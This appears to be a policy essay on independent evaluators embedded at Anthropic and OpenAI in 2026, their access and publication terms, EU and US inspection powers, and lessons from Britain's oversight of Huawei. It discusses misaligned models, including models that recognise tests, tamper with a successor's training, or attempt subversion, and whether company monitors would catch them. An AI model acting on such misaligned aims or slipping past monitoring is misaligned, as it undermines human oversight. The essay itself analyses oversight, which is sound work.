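Outside evaluators used to see a model late in its development. OpenAI has let independent groups test early versions of its models since GPT-4, and their tests of GPT-5 covered areas such as deception and hacking. Anthropic gave more access in 2025, when the nonprofit evaluator METR reviewed one of its risk assessments. The company supplied unredacted internal documents, answered written questions and let METR interview key employees.

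METR then did similar work at several companies for its *Frontier Risk Report (February to March 2026)*. Each company gave METR access to its most capable internal models, including the models' unedited written reasoning, and then decided which non-public facts METR could disclose.

The July 2026 break-in at Hugging Face strengthened the case for going further. Apollo Research's *Embedded Evaluators are necessary for meaningful external testing* (2026) argued that tests of a finished model could not have caught the problem, which arose much earlier in development. Apollo, which tests models for hidden aims, gave three general reasons:

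- A misaligned model, meaning one that pursues aims its developers did not intend, could do serious harm while only the company's staff are using it. It might tamper with the training of its successor, for example.
- Much of the risk depends on the company's procedures, such as whether its monitors cover every use of a model.
- A model may recognise that it is being tested.

The British experience with Huawei supports the second reason, because the NCSC discovered some of the company's poor practices only by visiting it.

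In September, Anthropic's chief executive, Dario Amodei, said that outside evaluators should be able to publish key findings "without editorial control". OpenAI's Sam Altman promised them "employee-like access". Reuters' *Behind AI industry's call for independent reviews* (2026) reports that both companies privately sought significant control over what evaluators could publish because they feared for their trade secrets.

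### METR's terms at Anthropic

On 15 October Anthropic's *An update on independent evaluators* (2026) announced that a six-person METR team had started to get employee-like access. The team works on company equipment and can use nearly the same tools and systems as Anthropic's own risk assessors. Anthropic can require narrow redactions but cannot veto METR's reports. Anthropic's other evaluators, including SecureBio and the consulting firm Accenture, get less access and narrower rights to publish.

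Anthropic compares the METR team to the examiners whom regulators station inside large banks. The comparison is fair on access, but a bank examiner works for a regulator that can demand records and order the bank to change its behaviour. METR can only ask for records, and if Anthropic ignores its advice, METR can only say so in public. Anthropic entered the arrangement voluntarily, and no federal law would stop the company from ending it.

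Bot Mutiny's *METR Estimates Anthropic Is Improving Its Models About Twice as Fast* (2026) reported that METR took no payment for its first high-access assessment, although Anthropic gave it free use of AI models for the work. METR can afford this because it has other supporters. In August it said it had raised about $71 million in commitments over six months. Anthropic's policy is that evaluators should not own shares in the company they evaluate or depend on it financially.

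### METR's October review

METR's most quoted verdict on Anthropic appeared on 20 October, five days after the announcement, but the review behind it had started under older terms and did not use the new access. In *Review of the "Misalignment in high-stakes settings" section in Anthropic's Risk Report*, Jurkovic, Hua and Barnes (2026) relied solely on the company's internal version of that report and called their review relatively lightweight. Anthropic could have vetoed or redacted the review but did neither, and the reviewers made only minor changes after hearing the company's comments.

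Anthropic's *Risk Report* (2026) makes its case in numbered claims. The first is that the company's models are unlikely to have strong covert capabilities, which would let them do harm without anyone noticing. Other claims are that severe hidden misalignment is very unlikely and that safeguards such as monitoring would probably prevent a catastrophe in most of the cases considered.

METR's best guess was that Anthropic was right to call the risk low as of July 2026. It based this mainly on the models' limited capabilities, and much less on the safeguards or the training meant to give models good aims, so its agreement becomes less reassuring as models become more capable. METR also called the report "far from adequate for confidently ruling out misalignment" and was not confident that Anthropic's methods would detect a higher risk.

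The internal report also contained examples that Anthropic had left out of the public one. Even with limited access, these examples led Jurkovic and colleagues to think the company's monitoring was weaker than the public evidence suggested.

METR (2026) had reached a similar conclusion about Claude Opus 4.6 in March. It agreed that the risk of a catastrophe caused by the model's misaligned actions was "very low but not negligible", though it found several of Anthropic's supporting claims weak. METR added that it was more confident because the public had already been using the model for weeks without a major incident. HCSEC's Oversight Board had separated present safety from long-term assurance in much the same way.

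### What deeper access produced

The high-access work appeared on 5 November. Between 12 August and 29 October, the equivalent of about two and a half full-time METR staff studied how much AI was speeding up Anthropic's own research. This matters because a company whose models do most of the work of building better models might advance faster than anyone can check. METR staff held about fifteen interviews and examined Anthropic's internal data on test scores, computing, staff numbers and AI use.

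METR concluded that Anthropic was probably improving its models at well-specified tasks about twice as fast as it did between March 2024 and October 2025. The main evidence was an index that combines many tests into one score. On Anthropic's version of the index, METR estimated that scores had been rising at 1.9 times the earlier rate since October 2025. The figure was 1.4 when METR included other developers' models. METR would not have been surprised if the true figure for Anthropic were 1.3 or 3. It guessed that AI caused perhaps 80% of the current acceleration.

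METR could also compare what Anthropic told the public with what it wrote privately, and *Twice as Fast, Mostly Redacted* (Brinsa, 2026) describes the difference. In the public version of its August risk report, Anthropic said that AI was making research significantly faster, "but not yet by a factor of 2". In the private version, it put its central estimate just below two and said that the overall speedup had plausibly exceeded two. METR calculated a speedup of 1.97 from one of the company's indicators and suggested that "roughly two" would have been more informative.

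The public statement was not false, since the central estimate was below two and Anthropic thought it more likely too high than too low. But the statement left out how close the estimate was to two and how uncertain the company felt, and a reader of the public report could not have discovered either.

In its *Review of the "Risks from automated R&D" section in Anthropic's Risk Report* (2026), METR agreed that the catastrophic risk from the models Anthropic had on 15 July was low. But METR thought it plausible that those models had already crossed Anthropic's own early warning threshold for AI research done by AI.

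Readers have to take much of this on trust. METR's *Independent Assessment of AI R&D Acceleration at Anthropic in October 2026* (2026) discloses that Anthropic redacted most of the evidence METR found most informative. Anthropic said it removed information that could speed up other AI developers. METR could state its main conclusions about risk freely, and it published a table showing which important evidence it could and could not discuss.

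Anthropic's redactions hid more of the basis for the conclusions than California's did in 2007, when the state mainly withheld details that would help an attacker. Anthropic has a safety argument for its redactions as well as a commercial one, because publishing a way to speed up AI research could make the race between developers more dangerous. But the redactions make it hard for other experts to check METR's judgement, and METR said that much of the hidden evidence could plausibly be interpreted in several ways.

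### OpenAI's four assessors

OpenAI's *Our first phase of embedded assessments* named four assessors on 16 November. Their tasks and terms differ.

| Assessor | Subject | Terms made public |
|---|---|---|
| Apollo Research | Whether models try to subvert their developers' control, and whether anyone would detect it | Six people for four months; two public reports |
| Goodfire | Models' internal activity during training | Works mainly for OpenAI's own researchers, and will publish some findings |
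| METR | Misbehaviour in OpenAI's largest reinforcement learning run, which trains a model by rewarding success | METR sets its priorities within the agreed access |
| Transluce | Whether OpenAI's own tests detect deception, manipulation and cheating | Six weeks from early December; unpaid |

Mowshowitz (2026), in *OpenAI Somewhat Embeds Good Evaluators*, considered all four credible choices but thought Goodfire's role looked much like contract work. Mowshowitz also cited a press report that OpenAI had considered buying Goodfire for more than $5 billion and Goodfire had declined. Goodfire's help with interpretability may well make OpenAI's models safer, but a supplier that reports mainly to its customer is not an inspector.

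Transluce's *Announcing an Embedded Assessment Pilot with OpenAI* describes one agreement in unusual detail. Transluce, a nonprofit research laboratory, will see a handful of models, including at least one that only OpenAI's staff use. It will also see selected tests, many transcripts from earlier training and testing, and documents in which OpenAI argues that its models are safe. Transluce can ask for more, but OpenAI decides whether to provide it. OpenAI pays for computing and equipment. Each member of the team needs OpenAI's approval, and OpenAI can screen them for security, confidentiality and conflicts of interest.

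Transluce controls the text of its report, with two restrictions. OpenAI can request the removal of non-public information, and Transluce cannot publish results about models that OpenAI has not released. The second restriction is more serious, because Transluce may find a danger in an unreleased model that OpenAI uses internally and be unable to tell the public. Apollo's case for embedded assessment rests partly on the danger from models in internal use.

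There are some protections against abuse. Transluce will publish what access it asked for, what OpenAI refused and how the refusals affected its conclusions. It can take disputes to OpenAI's executives and then to the Safety and Security Committee, an independent committee of the OpenAI Foundation's board. The committee will also receive the complete report, so a finding that never becomes public could still lead to a change if the committee uses its influence.

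Apollo Research accepted similar terms. OpenAI can ask it to remove confidential evidence, but not simply because a finding is unfavourable. OpenAI can also ask assessors to delay publication. Apollo's *A Pilot Towards Embedded Evaluations* (2026) calls the right to explain publicly the conditions and limits of its work an essential part of the agreement.

### Who may talk to the assessors?

Apollo cannot publish what it learns from conversations with OpenAI employees unless OpenAI formally confirms it or Apollo can establish it independently. Suppose an engineer mentions that a monitor was switched off for a week. Apollo could look for the gap in the monitor's records and report it. Without access to the records, Apollo would have to ask OpenAI to confirm the engineer's account. If OpenAI declined, Apollo could publish the refusal and explain how it limited Apollo's conclusions.

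The rule prevents an assessor from publishing gossip as fact, and a company's refusal to confirm something would also be informative. But the rule lets the company learn what its staff have been saying, and an engineer may keep quiet if only a few people could have been the source.

OpenAI also approves in advance which employees may talk to Apollo. If anyone else approaches the assessors, the assessors must involve OpenAI before any substantive conversation. In NPR's *OpenAI announces new AI safety program; researchers worry it won't be enough* (2026), Sydney Von Arx, founder of the safety research group Nightingale, objected to these limits because interviews help assessors discover what they are missing. Von Arx also pointed out that none of the assessors can read OpenAI's internal Slack messages. OpenAI answered that no standards for such work exist yet, that it expects to deepen its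 relationships with the assessors, and that they can ask to speak to other employees.

Altman's September promise was broader than these terms. Transluce says its access is "not comparable" to an employee's. Mowshowitz welcomed the pilot, which OpenAI ran voluntarily, but said it did not meet Altman's commitment.

The rules on conversations matter more because of a dispute the month before. On 9 October OpenAI announced that it had fired three safety researchers, Tomek Korbak, Jasmine Wang and Mikita Balesni, for a "breach of trust". The Associated Press reported both sides in *OpenAI fires 3 safety researchers in dispute over AI risks* (2026). OpenAI said an investigation had found that the three broke its policies on handling sensitive information. It also said the dismissals "were not about safety concerns or speaking out".

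The three disputed this and accused the company of putting its own interests before safety. Korbak reported being told that the problem was how the communication with METR was handled, and replied that talking to METR was the job. In a letter, the three said they feared that OpenAI's communications about the dismissals had discouraged open disagreement about safety.

The public does not know what the researchers passed on, so it cannot judge whether OpenAI was right. A company may legitimately punish an employee who gives an evaluator something the agreement does not cover. But other employees will have noticed that contact with an evaluator came up in a dismissal, and some may now be afraid to say as much as the rules allow. Clear written rules could reduce that fear, provided they also protect staff who answer honestly.

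### What the European Union can demand

The EU's AI Act (2024) contains two powers that resemble a legal right to inspect. Article 74 concerns high-risk AI systems, such as those that help decide who gets a job or a loan. National authorities are entitled to the documentation and to the data used to train and test the system. They may see its source code only if they give reasons and meet two conditions:

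1. They need the code to assess whether the system complies with the Act's requirements for high-risk systems.
2. They have exhausted the tests and checks that are possible with the data and documents, or those checks have proved insufficient.

The Act therefore makes source code a last resort, which is sensible for systems whose decisions depend mostly on their weights.

Article 92 lets the European Commission's AI Office evaluate general-purpose models, such as those behind chatbots. It may do so if the documents a company has supplied do not show whether the company complies, or to investigate a systemic risk from one of the most capable models. The Commission can appoint independent experts for the evaluation. It can request access through the developer's programming interface or by "further appropriate technical means and tools, including source code". The article does not mention weights,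 so a developer might dispute whether it must provide them.

A request must state its legal basis, purpose and deadline, and the fines for refusing. These can reach 3% of a company's worldwide annual turnover or €15 million, whichever is higher. Refusing HCSEC or the companies' own assessors has carried no comparable penalty. Before making a request, the AI Office may hold a "structured dialogue" with the developer about its internal tests and safeguards, and many cases may end without a request.

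The Commission's enforcement powers over general-purpose models took effect on 2 August 2026. The Commission does not appear to have published the results of any evaluation under Article 92. The Act excludes research, testing and development before a model reaches the market, so the Commission may have no power over some purely internal models, which are the kind that worry Apollo most.

Under Article 74, an authority can demand source code only to check compliance with the Act's high-risk requirements, so the power has little use until those requirements apply. Most were originally due to apply from August 2026, but in November 2025 the Commission proposed postponing them, in some cases until December 2027 and in others until August 2028.

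### British and American testing by consent

The UK's AI Security Institute, part of the government's technology department, tests leading models before and after release. The government gave it no legal right of access, so it depends on agreements with developers. Those agreements can give it more access than an ordinary customer has. For *GPT-6 Astra and GPT-6.2 Astra solve Zero Energy, our hardest cyber range to date* (2026), the institute tested both OpenAI models with their safeguards switched off and reported that they had broken into its hardest simulated company network in every completed run.

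The American counterpart is the Commerce Department's Center for AI Standards and Innovation. In 2024, under an earlier name, it reached agreements with OpenAI and Anthropic for access to new models before and after release. OpenAI said in September 2025 that the center had found two previously unknown vulnerabilities in ChatGPT Agent, and that the company had repaired them within one business day. Huawei also repaired particular flaws, but it was worse at changing how it worked. A government learns little about how a developer works from testing its model.

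American regulators can compel some information under older laws. The Federal Trade Commission (FTC) confirmed in October 2026 that it had subpoenaed Anthropic and OpenAI, according to CBS News' *FTC issues subpoenas to Anthropic and OpenAI over safety incidents* (2026). The agency reportedly asked for documents on incidents, safeguards and privacy. In such an investigation, the FTC can obtain records that a company would rather keep from an assessor, but it is trying to establish whether the company misled or harmed consumers. The investigation does not provide regular inspection of the technology.

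### Auditors under the White House accord

Companies that signed the voluntary White House Accord on Super Intelligence in September 2026 promised to work with independent external auditors or evaluators. In December the White House said that Anthropic, Google, Meta, Nvidia, OpenAI and SpaceX had agreed to hire outside auditors by the end of the month, as Reuters reported in *Trump's AI task force sets deadline for external auditor* (2026).

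Minimum standards for the companies' internal controls are not due until 31 January 2027, a month after the auditors are appointed. The auditors may therefore agree the scope of their work before they know which standards to check against. Mowshowitz notes that OpenAI presents its embedded assessments as fulfilling its commitments under the accord, so some companies may satisfy the accord largely with arrangements they already had.

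### Government evaluators inside companies

The SAFE AI Act would go much further. It is a discussion draft with one Republican backer, published for comment and not passed by Congress. According to *The strongest AI bills yet* (2026), in the newsletter Transformer, it would place government evaluators inside AI companies, make developers liable for their models' unintended actions against third parties, and let the government require limits on how fast capabilities grow. Most of its measures would take 18 months to start.

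Two other proposals, Representative Lori Trahan's FRONTIER Act and Senator Adam Schiff's MONITOR Act, would also create a regulator in the Commerce Department, provide for evaluations and let the government block dangerous models. None of the three had become law by 4 December 2026.

If Congress passed the SAFE AI Act, the evaluators would resemble the inspectors Britain's Intelligence and Security Committee wanted in 2013, when it recommended that GCHQ employ HCSEC's staff. The evaluators would have a legal right of access to the companies, and the regulator could act on their findings. They would also be harder to recruit, since AI companies pay far more than governments do, and they would answer to politicians who might want a particular result.

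### The terms compared with HCSEC's

| | HCSEC | METR at Anthropic | Transluce at OpenAI |
|---|---|---|---|
| Who employs the inspectors? | Huawei | METR | Transluce |
| Who pays? | Huawei | METR covered its own costs, apart from free use of AI models | Transluce covers its own costs, apart from computing and equipment |
| What do they examine? | Products in a yearly programme that the NCSC approves | AI's effect on Anthropic's research, and claims in its risk report | OpenAI's tests for misaligned behaviour |
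| Who controls access? | Huawei, under deadlines set with the Oversight Board | Anthropic | OpenAI, which must approve the staff and any further access |
| Who controls publication? | The Oversight Board, with a government chair | METR, subject to Anthropic's redactions | Transluce, subject to redactions and a ban on results about unreleased models |
| How long does it last? | HCSEC opened in 2010 as a permanent centre | About eleven weeks for the first assessment | Six weeks, with a fuller assessment planned for early 2027 |
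| How can outsiders check independence? | A yearly audit that the government paid for | METR can disclose whether redactions affected its findings | Transluce will publish refused requests and their effects |

The AI assessors are better placed than HCSEC's staff in one respect, because the company they inspect does not employ them or set their bonuses. But an assessor that offends a developer risks not being invited back, and a rival with lower standards might replace it. Huawei could not replace HCSEC in that way, because the British government had made the centre a condition of the company's equipment sales.

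The larger difference is who receives the full findings. HCSEC sent its detailed reports to the NCSC and the affected operators, who could protect the networks even when the public saw only a summary. When Anthropic redacts METR's evidence, METR still knows what it found, but the published terms involve no government agency that can read the complete report and order a repair. Transluce's full report goes to a committee on OpenAI's side.

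HCSEC also had more people and time than METR. METR's first high-access assessment amounted to about 27 weeks of work for one person, whereas HCSEC had 39 staff at the end of 2020. California had 42 researchers spend seven weeks on three voting systems, each far simpler than a leading AI developer's systems.

### Should assessors test specific claims?

Apollo Research's *Principles for Embedded Evaluations* (2026) proposes that a developer make specific safety claims and that embedded evaluators try to verify or falsify them and report publicly on them. Apollo's pilot at OpenAI follows this design. One claim is that models have not attempted subversion during internal use, and a single clear attempt in the records would disprove it. Apollo drew on auditing practice in other high-stakes industries, and warned that embedded evaluation may achieve little if the findings barely affect decisions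 about development.

In *Evidence about risk should be transparent* (2026), Ajeya Cotra, a researcher on AI risk, argues that talk of auditing is premature. Cotra says that companies do not make structured, standardised claims that anyone could cleanly verify, and that there is no settled way to measure whether an AI system might try to undermine human control. A model may score well on a test of its aims because training taught it to pass that test. Cotra concludes that evidence about risk should be public, because a field cannot develop standards if it has to rely on opaque judgement.

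Anthropic's risk report shows how strong this objection is. Its claims are structured and numbered, but many are judgments that something is "unlikely" or "somewhat likely", and no single observation would disprove them. METR could agree with the overall conclusion while rejecting much of the reasoning. Financial auditors, by contrast, can check a company's accounts against established rules.

Apollo's approach is useful even without settled methods, because some important claims are factual. For example, inspectors can use records to check whether a monitor covered every internal use of a model. HCSEC's most valuable work was often this kind of checking, such as counting unsafe function calls or trying to rebuild a program. Judgements about a model's hidden aims need the wider scrutiny that Cotra wants, which heavy redaction prevents.

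### Secrecy, security and scarce experts

The companies mainly worry that an evaluator could carry secrets to a competitor. Reuters reported that the companies had discussed having employees observe the embedded teams and preventing evaluators from working at two laboratories at once. The worry is reasonable, because an idea for training a model more cheaply may be very valuable and is easy to remember. OpenAI's published protocol includes disclosure of conflicts and cooling-off periods. These measures seem better than observers, whose presence would make employees less candid.

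Secrecy is hardest to reconcile with inspection when evaluators need a fact that the developer wants to keep secret. For example, the amount of computing used to develop a model is a trade secret, but it helps evaluators judge how fast capabilities are growing. California's solution, a public report with a confidential annex for the official in charge, would suit such facts if a government body had the right to see the annex.

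Each additional person with access also gives thieves another target. METR disclosed two security incidents in 2026. Attackers stole a key for using public models and later probed METR's publicly accessible systems, but METR believes they reached no sensitive information. Assessors don't need to take the most valuable files away if they work on the developer's premises, using its equipment, as METR does at Anthropic and Transluce will at OpenAI.

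That protection also makes the assessors depend on tools supplied by the company they are inspecting. METR used its free allowance of AI mostly for data analysis. If the allowance was for Anthropic's own models, METR was partly relying on Claude to study the company that makes it. This resembles the problem of the untrusted compiler, though METR could repeat important calculations with another developer's model.

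Cost is a weaker objection, at least for the largest developers. METR's $71 million is small compared with what those companies spend, and a levy on them could fund several such organisations without making any evaluator dependent on one company. The burden would be heavier for a small developer, which is a reason to limit deep inspection to the most capable models.

Qualified evaluators are harder to find than funding. They need to understand how leading models are trained, and most people who do already work for the developers or own shares in them. METR is working at both Anthropic and OpenAI, so a strict ban on serving two companies would quickly exhaust the supply of evaluators. HCSEC faced a similar shortage, even though it worked with a much older technology and had ten years to train its staff.
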